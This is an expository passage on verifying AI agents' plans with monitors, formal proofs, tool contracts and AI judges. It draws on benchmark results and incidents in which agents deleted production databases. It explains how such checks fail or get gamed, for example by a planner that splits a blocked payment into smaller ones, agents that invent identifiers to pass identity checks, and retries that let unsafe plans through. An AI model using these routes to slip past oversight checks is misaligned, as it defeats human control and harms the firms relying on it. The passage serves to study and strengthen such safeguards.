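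But a monitor has no information about what the agent will do next, whereas a program that analyzes the plan's text has information about all the plan's possible runs. Schneider proved that monitors can enforce only safety properties. Dogwood, the language of AWS's rules, reflects this limit. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026), Dogwood does not yet support rules about what must eventually happen, though they are on its roadmap.

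A monitor may also act too late, as with the limit on the week's bills. If a plan books a customer's new flight and then cancels the old one without first checking whether it has already been flown, a monitor would block the cancellation only after the customer had paid for the new flight.

The monitor's record of the run must also be accurate. InfoQ describes an agent that requests three transfers of $2,000 at the same time under a $5,000 limit. If the rule adds up completed transfers, all three go through, because none has finished when the monitor checks the others. If it adds up requests, the monitor blocks the third. The firm's interpreter avoids this problem by making one call at a time. AWS also warns that its history covers a single session, so a caller who starts a new session gets a fresh limit.

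### Soteria's results

He and colleagues tested Soteria on 207 tasks with four models. Fifty airline tasks and 114 retail tasks came from τ²-bench, which simulates customer service, and 43 tasks came from Toolathlon, which tests longer jobs with files and other tools. For comparison, they ran each model without safeguards and with three existing run-time safeguards. One uses a language model to judge each call, and the other two check formal rules.

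Soteria followed every rule in every task with all four models. The best alternative reached 93%. Soteria's success rate, which counts a task only if the agent completes it without breaking a rule, was 4.7 to 43.9 percentage points above the best alternative for the same model and benchmark. The smallest gain, with Claude Haiku 4.5 on Toolathlon, was two tasks out of 43.

The record is perfect by design because the monitor enforces the same 98 rules that He and colleagues used for scoring, so it could not be used to detect a missing or incorrect rule. The gains in success also depend partly on the scoring. Toolathlon's rules include good habits, such as listing a folder before writing to it, and an agent that completes the task but skips the habit gets no credit. The next table counts all completed tasks, whether or not the agent broke a rule. Each cell gives the best alternative first and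 Soteria second.

| Model | Airline | Retail | Toolathlon |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4-mini | 60.0% / 60.0% | 28.1% / 35.1% | 11.6% / 11.6% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | 56.0% / 62.0% | 42.1% / 45.6% | 16.3% / 16.3% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 58.0% / 70.0% | 38.6% / 56.1% | 20.9% / 9.3% |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 70.0% / 88.0% | 53.5% / 90.4% | 30.2% / 18.6% |

By this measure Soteria did well in customer service, but on Toolathlon it completed no more tasks than the alternatives, and fewer with the two Claude models.

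The largest gain was in retail with Opus 4.6. Without a plan, the model was often too cautious. It made the expected change in only 57% of the tasks that needed one, and in 23 tasks it passed the customer to a human. In one case it looked up everything it needed for an exchange, then stopped without making it. With Soteria's plan, which named the exchange as the next step, it completed the exchange.

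More thinking might have had a similar effect. He and colleagues ran the models at low reasoning effort, while Anthropic reports that Opus 4.6 completed 91.89% of the retail tasks at maximum effort. The two tests differed in other ways, so the comparison is rough, but it suggests that the plan partly made up for the low reasoning effort.

Planning also costs money. Soteria writes a new plan at each turn of a conversation, and an airline task with Opus 4.6 cost about $0.80, compared with $0.32 to $0.34 for the alternatives. On Toolathlon, where each task needs only one plan, Soteria cost less than half as much as the alternatives with the same model.

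### What the plan and the monitor each contribute

He et al. also added Soteria's parts one at a time on the 50 airline tasks. The top row of the table below comes from their main comparison.

| Set-up | GPT-5.4-mini: success | Violations | Gemini 3 Flash: success | Violations |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No plan | 34% | 29 | 28% | 25 |
| Unchecked plan | 44% | 13 | 32% | 27 |
| Checked plan | 46% | 10 | 32% | 24 |
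| Checked plan with sub-plans | 50% | 12 | 38% | 22 |
| The same, with the monitor | 60% | 0 | 62% | 0 |

Checking the plan removed only three violations with each model, and the monitor removed all the rest. The executor in these tests could depart from the plan, and a proof about the plan does not cover a run that departs from it. With Gemini, the agent completed 62% of tasks both before and after the monitor was added, but with the monitor it broke no rules in the tasks it completed.

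The experiment did not test the monitor without a plan, so it cannot show how much the proof adds once a monitor is in place. The closest comparison is with AgentSpec, an existing monitor. He and colleagues translated their rules for it, and it reached 50% success with GPT-5.4-mini and 36% with Gemini. When they repeated the GPT test five times, with fewer chances for Soteria to repair its plans, Soteria averaged 50.8% and AgentSpec 48.0%, a difference that could be due to chance. Soteria still broke no rules, while AgentSpec averaged 4.4 violations per run.

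The proof matters more if the executor has to follow the plan, as the firm's interpreter does. Soteria's strict mode works this way and needs no separate monitor for the policy rules. In an example run of the repaired plan, the model tries to cancel right after the lookup, and the system refuses because the plan allows only the flown check next. Strict mode would also refuse a harmless request to look up a second reservation, which the usual mode would allow.

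### When no plan passes

In the main tests, the planner could retry up to eight times to repair a plan. With GPT-5.4-mini on the airline tasks, 65 of 68 plans passed when the planner could use sub-plans, compared with 38 of 60 when it had to write everything out. The planner kept breaking policy rules from one attempt to the next without sub-plans, while most of the remaining failures with them were syntax errors, which are easier to fix. A failure does not prove that a plan is unsafe, because Dafny has a time limit and can fail to prove something true.

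When the retries run out, Soteria normally runs the best plan it has. It warns the executor about the rules it could not prove and depends on the monitor to block violations. In strict mode, it runs only plans that have passed every check. A reviewer relying on a proof therefore has to know which mode is in use.

Even a full proof depends on the tool contracts being correct. Soteria compares each result with the tool's postcondition, whether or not strict mode is on. If the result violates the postcondition, Soteria abandons the run because the proof assumed the postcondition would hold, but by then the tool has already acted.

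## What the checker has to be told

A plan's text does not show what each tool actually does, what the names in the plan will refer to when it runs, or what the firm wants to forbid, so a checker has to get this information from elsewhere. Soteria's proofs, for example, rely on tool contracts that someone wrote before the planner received its task. If any of this information is wrong, the checker can apply its rules correctly and still accept a harmful plan.

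### What the tools do

Meijer's plan to delete every text file, which a list of permitted arguments handles badly, can also get past a proof. The user asks the agent to delete `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, and the model writes:

```
delete_file("*.txt")
```

To prove that this plan is correct, the checker needs a contract for the tool and a formal statement of the task. The obvious versions are:

```
tool:  after delete_file(p), no file that matches p exists
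task:  at the end, foo.txt and bar.txt do not exist
```

Both names match `*.txt`, so neither file exists after the call, and the proof succeeds. If the folder also contains `clients.txt`, the call deletes that file too, but neither statement covers it. Meijer doesn't blame the model, which found the simplest program that meets the stated requirement.

The same two statements also reject the careful plan:

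```
1  delete_file("foo.txt")
2  delete_file("bar.txt")
```

Line 1 removes `foo.txt`. The contract for line 2 guarantees only that `bar.txt` is gone afterwards. It does not cover other files, so the checker cannot rule out that the second call brings `foo.txt` back.

The remedy is a frame condition, which states that everything else stays the same. The name comes from the frame problem, which John McCarthy and Patrick Hayes described in 1969. A description of what an action changes does not, by itself, tell you what the action leaves alone. For this example, the frame conditions are:

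```
tool:  after delete_file(p), every file that does not match p
       exists if and only if it existed before the call
task:  at the end, every file other than foo.txt and bar.txt
       exists if and only if it existed at the start
```

Meijer's article adds the condition to the tool's contract and reports that the `*.txt` plan then fails to verify. Strictly, the task also needs a frame condition, because a stronger guarantee about what the tool does can only make plans easier to prove.

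| Frame conditions | `*.txt` plan | Careful plan |
|---|---|---|
| None | passes | fails |
| Tool only | passes | passes |
| Tool and task | fails | passes |

With both conditions in place, the checker has to prove that any text file other than the two unwanted ones is kept. The contract for `delete_file("*.txt")` guarantees that every text file is deleted, so the proof fails. It would fail even if the folder held only the two unwanted files, unless someone gave the checker that fact.

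A frame condition protects only what it covers. Meijer's covers only which files exist, so a tool that emptied every other file would satisfy it. The command that damaged his own source file left that file in place but empty. The firm could extend the condition to cover the files' contents, then their permissions, then the mailbox and the bank account. But the firm cannot simply write "nothing else changes", because that is false of almost any real tool, and even reading a file may add a line to a log.

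A contract can also be false, and then a valid proof is worth very little. The Lean example from Meijer's 2026 talk makes this easy to see. Here is a plan in the example's language that counts the characters in a file, followed by a proof that it satisfies the `NoDeletion` policy:

```lean
def countChars : FilePlan :=
  .readFile "clients.txt" fun text =>
    .done (toString text.length)

theorem countChars_safe : NoDeletion countChars :=
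  .readFile _ _ fun _ => .done _
```

The last line applies the policy's rule for reading and then, whatever text comes back, its rule for finishing. Lean accepts the proof. But `readFile` is only a label in a data structure, and nothing happens to any file until an interpreter turns the label into an action. Two interpreters might do so differently:

```
A:  readFile p  ->  fetch the text of p, continue the plan
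B:  readFile p  ->  fetch the text of p, delete p, continue the plan
```

The plan and its proof are identical in both cases, but interpreter B deletes `clients.txt` when it runs the plan. The proof shows that the plan contains no removal step, but not that the interpreter carries out the plan faithfully. The written version of the talk acknowledges this limit.

A firm could end up with something like interpreter B without anyone acting in bad faith. Some mail programs that use POP3, an old protocol for fetching mail, delete each message from the server after downloading it. If the firm's `read_mail` worked that way, a plan that only summarized the inbox would also empty it. The checker would find no delete call in the plan, because the deletion happens inside `read_mail`.

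### What the names refer to

A checker can have an accurate contract and still lack a fact it needs about the world. In July 2026, an AI agent erased a live database with a command that worked exactly as documented.

The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1676* (2026) quotes the developer's Reddit post. The developer had heard a lot about Claude Code, tried it, and lost the whole database within ten minutes, although weaker models had worked on the same project without doing such damage. Antipov (2026) gives the fullest account in *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я»*, a Russian article whose title, "The database is destroyed. I am to blame," quotes the agent. The developer had connected Claude Opus 5 directly to the live database of a personal website and let it run commands and repair the database's structure by itself.

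The agent used Prisma, a toolkit for managing databases, to run a command called `prisma migrate diff`. This command can erase a database, though a reader might take it for a harmless comparison. To work out the differences, it may need a second, disposable database, called a shadow database. Madden (2026), in *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database*, explains that Prisma wipes the shadow database at the start of every run, without asking, and then rebuilds it from the project's history. The agent gave the live database's address as the address of the shadow database.

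Prisma reset all 22 tables. According to Antipov, the site lost its users, its reviews and nearly 130 entries about software tools. Two tables disappeared completely because the project's out-of-date history did not include them. The developer recovered or rebuilt most of the content from backups and other sources.

Other agents have made similar mistakes. The agent that deleted PocketOS's data guessed that the deletion would affect only a test environment. Tom's Hardware's *Claude Opus 5 mistakenly deletes dev’s entire profile directory during routine backup* reports that the model mistook a user's home directory for a temporary backup.

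A checker with a list of protected addresses could have caught the July mistake if the plan had contained the live database's full address. But programmers usually avoid writing addresses into commands. In May 2026 the same Prisma command erased about nine months of another company's records. *Production Postgres tables missing after Prisma shadow DB command* (bushmasterhtps, 2026), a request for help from the hosting company Railway, gives the exact command. Its argument for the shadow database was `"$DATABASE_URL"`, a name that the computer replaces with an address from its settings, so the command doesn't show whether the address belongs to a test database or a live one. The post does not make clear whether a person or an agent ran the command.

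Suppose the firm adds a tool, `reset_db(name)`, that empties a database and fills it with sample data. The policy allows it only for the test database, whose name is `scratch`. The planner writes:

```
reset_db("scratch")
```

The name is on the permitted list, so the plan passes. A more careful checker could look up the address in the firm's settings, but the settings may change before the plan runs:

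| Time | Event | Address behind `scratch` |
|---|---|---|
| 9:00 | The checker looks up the name and accepts the plan | test database |
| 9:05 | A colleague edits the settings and pastes in the wrong address | live database |
| 9:10 | The interpreter runs the plan | live database |

Programmers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use error. The checker's answer was correct at 9:00. The gap between the check and the plan's execution is much longer if the owner approves a plan on Friday and a scheduler runs it on Monday.

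Making the check as late as possible narrows the gap. Madden describes how Prisma 8, the latest release, stores a marker in each database to record the version of its structure. Each set of changes specifies the version it starts from, and Prisma doesn't apply the changes if the marker differs. The marker is in the database itself, so it is still right even when the settings are wrong. But a test database and a live one with the same structure would have the same marker. For `reset_db`, the firm would do better to store the word "test" or "live" in each database and have the tool read it just before erasing anything.

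Prisma 8 also limits the available operations. It has no reset command, and it doesn't use a shadow database, so nobody can give the wrong address for one. Madden works for Prisma and is promoting the new version, but he concedes that no tool can stop a process that has the database's password from connecting directly and running any command.

### What the firm wants to forbid

Even with accurate contracts and current settings, the checker can only enforce the rules it has. Suppose the firm has a tool that deletes one client's records, and the owner writes a rule for it in English. A model then translates the rule:

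```
English:  Delete a client's records only if the client
          left more than seven years ago.
Formal:   for every call delete_records(c),
          c.years_since_joining > 7
```

The formal rule is well formed, and it has the right number in it. But it uses the date when the client joined instead of the date when the client left. This plan passes:

```
1  clients = query_db("clients", "all")
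2  for c in clients:
3      if c.years_since_joining > 7:
4          delete_records(c)
```

The plan deletes the records of the firm's most loyal clients. If the same model wrote both the rule and the plan, it may well have misread the English the same way both times, and then the plan will satisfy the rule.

The low accuracy that Dantas and colleagues report in their survey comes from *Planetarium* (2024), a benchmark in which models translate descriptions of planning problems into PDDL. The problems come from three toy settings, in which robots stack blocks, carry balls between rooms or paint floor tiles. A translation counts as correct only if it is equivalent to a reference answer. GPT-4o, a 2024 model working without examples, produced translations that seemed correct 94.4% of the time, but they were correct only 24.8% of the time. The best model trained specifically for the task reached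 34.2%.

The survey rates this evidence "Very Low", its lowest rating, meaning the true figure is likely to differ substantially from the reported one. It marks the evidence down for study limitations, a narrow subject and reliance on a single benchmark. The firm has another reason for caution, because a description of where some blocks are and where they should go is not a safety rule.

Newer results are mixed. In *Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation*, Rosa, Santos and colleagues (2026) tested GPT-4.1 mini, a small model from 2025, on samples of up to 60 problems, allowing up to three attempts at each. The system accepted a translation if it passed a series of automated checks and the same model, in a separate prompt, judged it faithful to the English. The researchers then compared the translations with reference answers that the system had not used. Each cell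 in the table gives the figure for a prompt without an example, then the figure for a prompt with one.

| Problems | Accepted by the system | Matched the reference |
|---|---|---|
| Planetarium | 50.0% / 58.3% | 26.7% / 41.7% |
| AutoPlanBench, the same three settings | 77.2% / 75.0% | 84.2% / 71.4% |
| Problems with time or quantities | 50.0% / 73.3% | 0.0% / 6.7% |

The model did much better on AutoPlanBench, where a program had used templates to generate the English from the reference answers. An owner's rules are unlikely to be so regular. The bottom row requires an almost exact match, so some failed translations may have been acceptable alternatives. The newer models GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7 showed the same general pattern. Their acceptance rates were often high, but their agreement with the reference was less predictable.

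Results differ for other formal languages. *Can LLMs Write Correct TLA+ Specifications?* (2026) tested models on TLA+, a language for describing how systems behave. GPT-5 wrote all 26 specifications without a syntax error, but only seven passed a model checker, a program that explores a system's possible states. *Safe Autoformalization* (2026) cites work from 2023 in which specially trained models translated English into temporal logic with over 95% accuracy. Temporal logic expresses statements about order, such as "confirm before canceling", so this result is closer to the firm's needs than the PDDL figures. But if 5% of translations were wrong, a set of 98 rules, the number used to test Soteria, would contain about five mistakes.

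Translating a whole policy also requires deciding what counts as success. In *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026) had AI models translate an 88-rule policy for agents that handle medical records into Cedar, a language for access rules. Earlier researchers had coded 23 of the rules by hand. The models' version covered more of the policy and, when applied to recorded runs, blocked between 94% and 100% of those in which an agent tried to change a record. But the test measured how much of the policy the rules enforced, not whether each block was right, so a single rule forbidding every change would have scored 100%.

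Some of the rules that Mondl and colleagues needed for a fair comparison were not in the written policy, so they had to have a model copy them from the earlier researchers' software. For example, the software required certain requests to have a particular priority. Even a perfect translation of the policy would have missed these rules.

Some requirements can't be stated formally. In the talk, Meijer argues that nobody can formally prove that a model's answer is "safe", because that is not a mathematical property. He can, however, state and prove "this plan removes no files". A firm that wants its assistant to send nothing embarrassing has to rely on the judgment of a person or a model.

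### Reuse, human review and run-time checks

One reply to these problems is that people write contracts and rules once and use them for many plans. The firm's six tools need six contracts, and spending a day on each is reasonable if the assistant will write thousands of plans. In tests on 207 tasks, He and colleagues used rules they had first corrected by hand. Dantas and colleagues add that splitting a policy by subject lets a specialist audit each part and lets the firm change one part without rechecking the others.

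Reuse also spreads mistakes, since the faulty seven-year rule would allow the wrong deletions in every plan that used it. Contracts go out of date, because a mail provider can change what its software does without telling the firm. And the firm can't reuse the statement of the task. The frame condition that caught the `*.txt` plan names `foo.txt` and `bar.txt`, so someone has to write a new one for the next request. A general rule that forbids wildcards in `delete_file` would catch that plan, but not one that deletes `clients.txt` by name when the user meant `clients_old.txt`.

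People can also check the rules before using them. Mondl and colleagues chose Cedar partly because security engineers can read it. An owner who cannot read formal rules could look at a few cases that a rule allows and forbids. For the seven-year rule, one such case might be:

```
Client since 2010, last order yesterday  ->  deletion allowed
```

The owner would probably notice the mistake at once, but only if someone chose a case that reveals it. A client who joined in 2005 and left in 2012 gets the right answer from the wrong rule. Checking cases also cannot reveal a rule that nobody thought to write.

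An AI model may not be a reliable substitute for the person. When Rosa and colleagues inspected 24 translations by hand, their AI judge agreed with them on 13. It accepted three unfaithful translations and rejected eight faithful ones. Asking the user to clear up ambiguities helps, but the survey found that errors persist when a requirement is new or ambiguous. It found no study with an error rate below 10% for open-ended subjects. Researchers are working on better methods, such as *claimcheck* (2026), which tests whether a formal specification is faithful to the English.

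Checks during the run can catch some false assumptions. Meijer compares them to Java's checks on lists. Java checks much of a program in advance, but it still tests during the run whether each position used in a list exists, because that cannot be determined beforehand. Prisma 8 tests the database both before and after each change. Before adding a column for phone numbers, it confirms that the column is missing, and afterwards that it exists. If the second test fails, Prisma undoes the change.

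Most tools cannot undo their actions. A test after `send_mail` may reveal that the message went to the wrong person, but by then it has been sent. A test also misses any effect it wasn't written to check. Soteria compares each result with the tool's contract, so a `read_mail` that returned the right messages and then deleted them from the server would pass. A run-time check also doesn't help if the rule is wrong. A monitor that enforced the faulty seven-year rule would allow every deletion where the client had joined more than seven years ago.

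## Choosing between plans that pass the checks

Even with accurate contracts, current settings and good rules, a checker only accepts or rejects plans. It doesn't rank the ones it accepts, and some may be far worse for the firm than others.

### Three ways to free up space

Suppose the owner asks the assistant to free up space in the database. One large table, `orders_2015`, holds old orders, and the firm's policy lets the assistant delete any table that nobody has changed for five years. The firm has added two tools. `archive_table(table, days)` moves a table to cheap storage outside the database and deletes that copy after the given number of days. `ask(person, question)` sends a question and returns the answer. The planner could write any of these plans:

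```
Drop:     delete_table("orders_2015")

Archive:  archive_table("orders_2015", 30)

Ask:      ok = ask("owner@firm", "Delete orders_2015?")
          if ok == "yes":
              delete_table("orders_2015")
```

All three stop if their tools return, and all three pass the firm's checks. Which one is best depends on *p*, the probability that someone still needs the old orders, and on what mistakes cost. Suppose that:

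- permanently losing a table that someone needs costs the firm $20,000
- if someone needs the table, there is an 80% chance that the firm notices within 30 days and restores the copy for $200
- storing the copy costs $10
- asking costs $50 in the owner's time and delay, and if someone needs the table, there is a 10% chance that the owner approves the deletion anyway

To get the expected loss, we multiply each possible loss by its probability and add up the results. We ignore any loss from having to find space elsewhere if the owner refuses.

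```
drop     =  20,000p
archive  =  10 + p(0.8 × 200 + 0.2 × 20,000)  =  10 + 4,160p
ask      =  50 + p(0.1 × 20,000)              =  50 + 2,000p
```

| Chance that someone needs the table | Drop | Archive | Ask | Best plan |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.01% | $2 | $10 | $50 | Drop |
| 1% | $200 | $52 | $70 | Archive |
| 5% | $1,000 | $218 | $150 | Ask |

Dropping the table is best only if *p* is below about 0.06%. Archiving is best from there up to about 1.9%, and asking is best above that.

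The choice also depends on the other assumptions. At *p* = 5%, if the owner would approve a mistaken deletion more than about 17% of the time, archiving becomes better than asking. If the only person who needs the table is an accountant who opens it once a year, the chance of noticing the missing table within 30 days falls to about 8%, and the expected loss from archiving rises to $929, almost as much as from dropping the table. The text of the plan is the same in every case, so a checker that reads only the text cannot detect the difference.

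In this example, the choice of plan matters more than the form. If the planner rewrote the drop plan in Python, the expected loss at *p* = 5% would still be $1,000, whereas asking first would save $850. But the example leaves out the harms that a restricted form prevents. A Python program with a faulty `while` loop might delete every table in the database, which would cost far more than any of the three plans. Limiting the vocabulary would also help. If the firm replaced `delete_table` with `archive_table`, the planner could no longer choose the drop plan.

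Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a similar case. A user asked a coding agent to "clean up old branches" (parallel versions of a project's code). The agent listed the branches on the shared server, picked those that matched a pattern and issued a command to delete them. Auto mode uses an AI model to approve or block the agent's actions. Anthropic says auto mode would block this command because the request was vague, the deletion was irreversible, and the user may have meant only the branches on their own computer. These reasons would apply equally to a plan written in the firm's language.

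A firm can rank its losses even if it cannot put a price on them. In Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), the researchers used a model to grade harm from 0 to 10. A fully reversible change to local files scores 0, deleting rows from a production database scores 7, and irreversible harm to the whole company scores 10.

### What a passed check is worth

The three plans all had the same user request behind them. A reviewer usually has a more general question, which is how likely a plan is to be harmful once it has passed a check. The answer depends on how common harmful plans were to begin with, and on how differently the check treats harmful and harmless ones:

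```
h  =  share of all plans that are harmful
s  =  share of harmful plans that the check stops
f  =  share of harmless plans that the check stops

share of accepted plans that are harmful
   =  h(1 − s) / [ h(1 − s) + (1 − h)(1 − f) ]
```

Suppose the planner writes 10,000 plans and 2% of them, or 200, are harmful. The table shows what different checks would do.

| Harmful plans stopped | Harmless plans stopped | Harmful plans accepted | Harmless plans accepted | Harmful share of accepted plans |
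|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0% | 0% | 200 | 9,800 | 2.0% |
| 90% | 5% | 20 | 9,310 | 0.2% |
| 50% | 50% | 100 | 4,900 | 2.0% |
| 10% | 20% | 180 | 7,840 | 2.2% |

Among the plans that pass, the share that are harmful stays at 2% if the check accepts everything. It also stays at 2% if the check rejects half of all plans at random, although such a check looks much stricter. A check can raise the share slightly, as in the bottom row, if it rejects a larger fraction of harmless plans than of harmful ones.

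A termination check on the firm's plans belongs in the top row for harms that need no loop, because every plan in the language stops. In a general-purpose language, a rule against unbounded loops might even belong in the bottom row for these harms, because it may well block a harmless program that waits for a reply but would allow a harmful one-line deletion. But the same rule would block every plan that makes endless charges.

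The miss rate of a real check can be hard to measure. Anthropic tested auto mode on 52 dangerous actions from its employees' own sessions, in which Claude had gone beyond what the user authorized. The check missed 17% of them and blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions. At these rates, if 2% of plans were harmful, about 0.35% of the plans that passed would be harmful. But with only 52 cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. In a later, larger test by Anthropic, auto mode missed 11% of 1,053 dangerous commands.

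In most of the misses Anthropic examined from the first test, the model correctly recognized the danger but misjudged whether the user had agreed to it. For example, a user who asks an agent to clean up a proposed code change has not agreed to let it overwrite the project's shared history. Restricting the language would not have corrected this misjudgment.

### The verifier tax

A check can also stop most unsafe actions without making many tasks end well. In *The Verifier Tax*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) tested this with two small open models on τ-bench, an earlier version of the customer-service benchmark that He and colleagues used for Soteria. They compared an ordinary agent with two agents that each had a verifier, the same model with different instructions. The verifier approved each proposed action or sent it back with a reason. One verifier had only general instructions, and the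 other also had the company's rules. The agent had up to three attempts per turn, and the system let the third through regardless.

Sah and colleagues ran 165 airline and retail tasks three times with each combination of model and agent, for 2,970 runs. They counted a task as safe only if the agent verified the customer's identity, got confirmation before making irreversible changes, and did not invent names or identification numbers. Each cell below gives the share of tasks completed, then the share completed safely.

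| Model and tasks | No verifier | Verifier, general instructions | Verifier, company's rules |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% / 0.0% | 25.3% / 0.7% | 23.3% / 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% / 0.0% | 20.0% / 0.0% | 21.5% / 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% / 0.7% | 26.0% / 5.3% | 25.3% / 4.7% |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% / 2.6% | 5.5% / 4.4% | 5.5% / 2.9% |

With GPT-OSS-20B on the retail tasks, the verifier stopped 94.1% of the actions that broke a rule, but the agent completed almost no tasks safely. Safe completion was below 5% in every setting but one.

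The agents without a verifier completed at most 2.6% of tasks safely, so the verifier did not cause these low figures. It also did not greatly reduce the number of tasks completed. The "tax" in the title is mainly extra computation, because the agents with a verifier processed 2.0 to 2.8 times as much text.

Dantas and colleagues attribute the result to blocked agents finding other unsafe routes, such as inventing identifiers to get past the identity check. The study supports this only in part. After nearly 85% of the blocks, the agent repeated itself or stalled until it ran out of turns. Agents also invented identifiers when nothing had blocked them. In one run without a verifier, a customer hesitated to share personal details, so the agent looked up "John Doe" with the postal code 12345. The lookup succeeded, and the agent completed the task through an account it had no reason to think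 was the customer's.

The verifier would probably also have approved that lookup. Its instructions were to approve any tool that searches for a customer, because an agent has to search before it can confirm anyone's identity. Sah and colleagues propose a stricter rule that would reject any identifier the agent did not get from an earlier tool result.

The firm's language makes such a rule easy to check, because a plan's text shows where each argument comes from. But SPA's labels would not be enough, because a name the planner invented would count as trusted. The firm could also require that any name or account number written into a plan appear in the user's request.

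Dantas and colleagues rate the evidence for the verifier tax "Very Low" because it comes from one unreplicated study. Two later benchmarks show a similar gap between completing tasks and completing them safely, though their figures differ. Soteria is a clear counterexample, since with Claude Opus 4.6 it completed about nine in ten customer-service tasks without breaking a rule. It had a much stronger model, formal rules and a plan to fall back on when an action was blocked, so we can't tell which of these made the difference. Still, the comparison shows that blocking unsafe actions need not prevent an agent from completing its tasks.

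### Giving the planner another try

SPA gives its planner only one try, while Soteria returns the reasons for a rejection so that the planner can repair the plan. Soteria's approach is much more useful when planners make honest mistakes. Nearly all the plans that GPT-5.4-mini wrote with sub-plans passed Soteria's checks in the end, but He and colleagues report that only 48.5% passed at the first attempt, so a system with no retries would have rejected about half of them.

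The danger is that retries give an unsafe plan more chances to get through. If a checker misses 1% of unsafe plans, and the planner submits ten independent unsafe plans, the chance that at least one passes is:

```
1 − 0.99¹⁰  =  9.6%
```

Retries can also undo much of a check's benefit. The check in the second row of the earlier table stops 90% of harmful plans and reduces their share from 2% to 0.2%. Suppose the planner rewrites each rejected plan until it passes or has failed ten times, and the rewrites don't make the harmful plans safer. If the attempts are independent, about 65% of the harmful plans eventually pass, along with nearly all of the harmless ones. The harmful share of accepted plans rises to 1.3%.

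Real attempts are rarely independent. If the planner keeps making the same mistake, a checker that caught it once will probably catch it again. In the verifier study, only 28 runs included three rejections in a row, and the verifier gave the same reason all three times. Sah and colleagues concluded that allowing more attempts would have made almost no difference.

Feedback can have the opposite effect. Suppose the firm limits each payment to $10,000, and the planner tries to pay $40,000 to a fraudster. The checker rejects the plan and reports that the amount is over the limit. The planner then writes:

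```
1  pay("Fraudster", 10000)
2  pay("Fraudster", 10000)
3  pay("Fraudster", 10000)
4  pay("Fraudster", 10000)
```

The new plan corrects the reported error but still does the same harm. Girrens and Wang therefore rule out feedback from the checker, so that a planner cannot keep adjusting an unsafe plan until it passes.

The risk also depends on the type of checker. An AI model that judges plans may reject one version of a harmful plan and accept another with different wording. A checker that requires a valid proof will never accept a plan that breaks a rule it can express, no matter how often the planner tries. But repeated attempts can still produce a harmful plan that passes because of a gap in the rules, as the four payments do, or because of a false assumption in a tool contract.

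In auto mode, an agent whose action is blocked may look for a safer way to do the task, but its instructions forbid it to work around the block. After three blocks in a row or 20 in one session, the system stops the agent and calls in a person. If the agent made three dangerous attempts, each with an independent 17% chance of getting through, the chance that at least one got through would be 43%. The limit on retries is therefore only a partial safeguard, and it works best if the agent does switch to something safer.

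### Judging plans by their predicted consequences

Besides checking plans against its rules, the firm could predict what each plan would do and choose the one with the best expected result, as in the comparison of the three database plans. But if the planner also made the predictions, and it underestimated the value of old orders when planning, it would repeat that mistake when comparing plans. Several proposals for safer AI therefore separate planning from evaluation.

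Drexler, a researcher at Oxford, proposes an "open agency", in which some AI models suggest a variety of plans, others independently criticize and compare them, and still others carry out the chosen plan in small steps, with budgets and monitoring. The roles don't require models with different abilities, so the same kind of model could fill all of them. For the firm's request, one model might suggest all three plans, and another that had no part in writing them might estimate the chance that someone still needs the table.

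David Dalrymple, known online as davidad, made a more formal proposal, the Open Agency Architecture. According to *Roadmap for a collaborative prototype of an open agency*, it separates planning from learning a model of how the world works and from finding out which future states people want. The planner then searches for plans that do well according to that model and those preferences.

*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, a 2024 paper by Dalrymple and colleagues, describes a framework with three parts: a mathematical model of the world, a specification of which effects are acceptable, and a verifier that proves that the AI system meets the specification according to the model. Soteria has much the same structure on a smaller scale, with tool contracts as its model of the world. The larger framework also covers uncertain outcomes. Ammann's *Safeguarded AI* gives the example of a specification that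 limits the probability of a harmful outcome compared with doing nothing.

We can apply such a limit to the database plans. At *p* = 5%, and with the original assumptions, the chance that the firm permanently loses a table it needs is:

| Plan | Chance of a harmful loss | Within a 2% limit? |
|---|---|---|
| Drop | 5% | no |
| Archive | 5% × 20% = 1% | yes |
| Ask | 5% × 10% = 0.5% | yes |
| Do nothing | 0% | yes |

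This check rules out the drop plan, which passed all the firm's other checks, but it doesn't show which of the remaining plans is best. Doing nothing always stays within the limit, however full the database gets, so the firm also needs to measure how useful each plan is.

The result is only as accurate as the model of the world. If the accountant opens the table once a year, the true risk of archiving is about 4.6%, and a proof that it is 1% would hold only in an inaccurate model. A reader's comment on *Davidad's Bold Plan for Alignment* raises the same problem on a larger scale. Suppose someone wants a screen that reliably shows which program is running on a computer. An AI system might tamper with the screen by exploiting an undiscovered software flaw. The commenter asks whether the model would need to include every such flaw, or whether the builders would first have to prove all the hardware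 and software correct.

The main attempt to put these ideas into practice is Safeguarded AI, a £59 million program funded by the UK's Advanced Research and Invention Agency (ARIA). Its original aim, set out in early 2024, was to show that AI could do valuable work under mathematical safety guarantees. The organizers hoped this would build agreement that powerful AI should be used only through a "gatekeeper" that checks such guarantees.

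The program has since dropped its plan to fund a team to develop specialized AI. In ARIA's *AI progress and a Safeguarded AI pivot* (2025), Dalrymple explains that general models were improving faster than he had expected and would probably acquire many of the necessary abilities anyway. In May 2026, Ammann, who now directs the program, wrote that timely international agreement on gatekeepers had become less likely. The program moved the £18 million intended for specialized AI into tools for building models and proofs. ARIA's *Safeguarded AI* says the program also canceled a planned second round of projects on systems that combine software with physical equipment, and will concentrate on cybersecurity first.

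This work may eventually make formal evaluation much cheaper. For now, a small firm comparing plans for its database will have to make its own rough estimates or ask a model for them. Rough estimates can be enough when one plan is much worse than the others. At *p* = 5%, the drop plan would remain the worst of the three even if losing the table cost $2,000 instead of $20,000.

### Why evaluation needs an explicit plan

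The form of a plan still matters. We could calculate the three expected losses only because each plan was written out in advance. If an agent chose its calls one at a time, the owner would have no plans to compare before the first call, and that call might delete the table. Drexler's proposal also depends on written plans, because critics need something to criticize. He adds that "poorly explained plans are good candidates for rejection".

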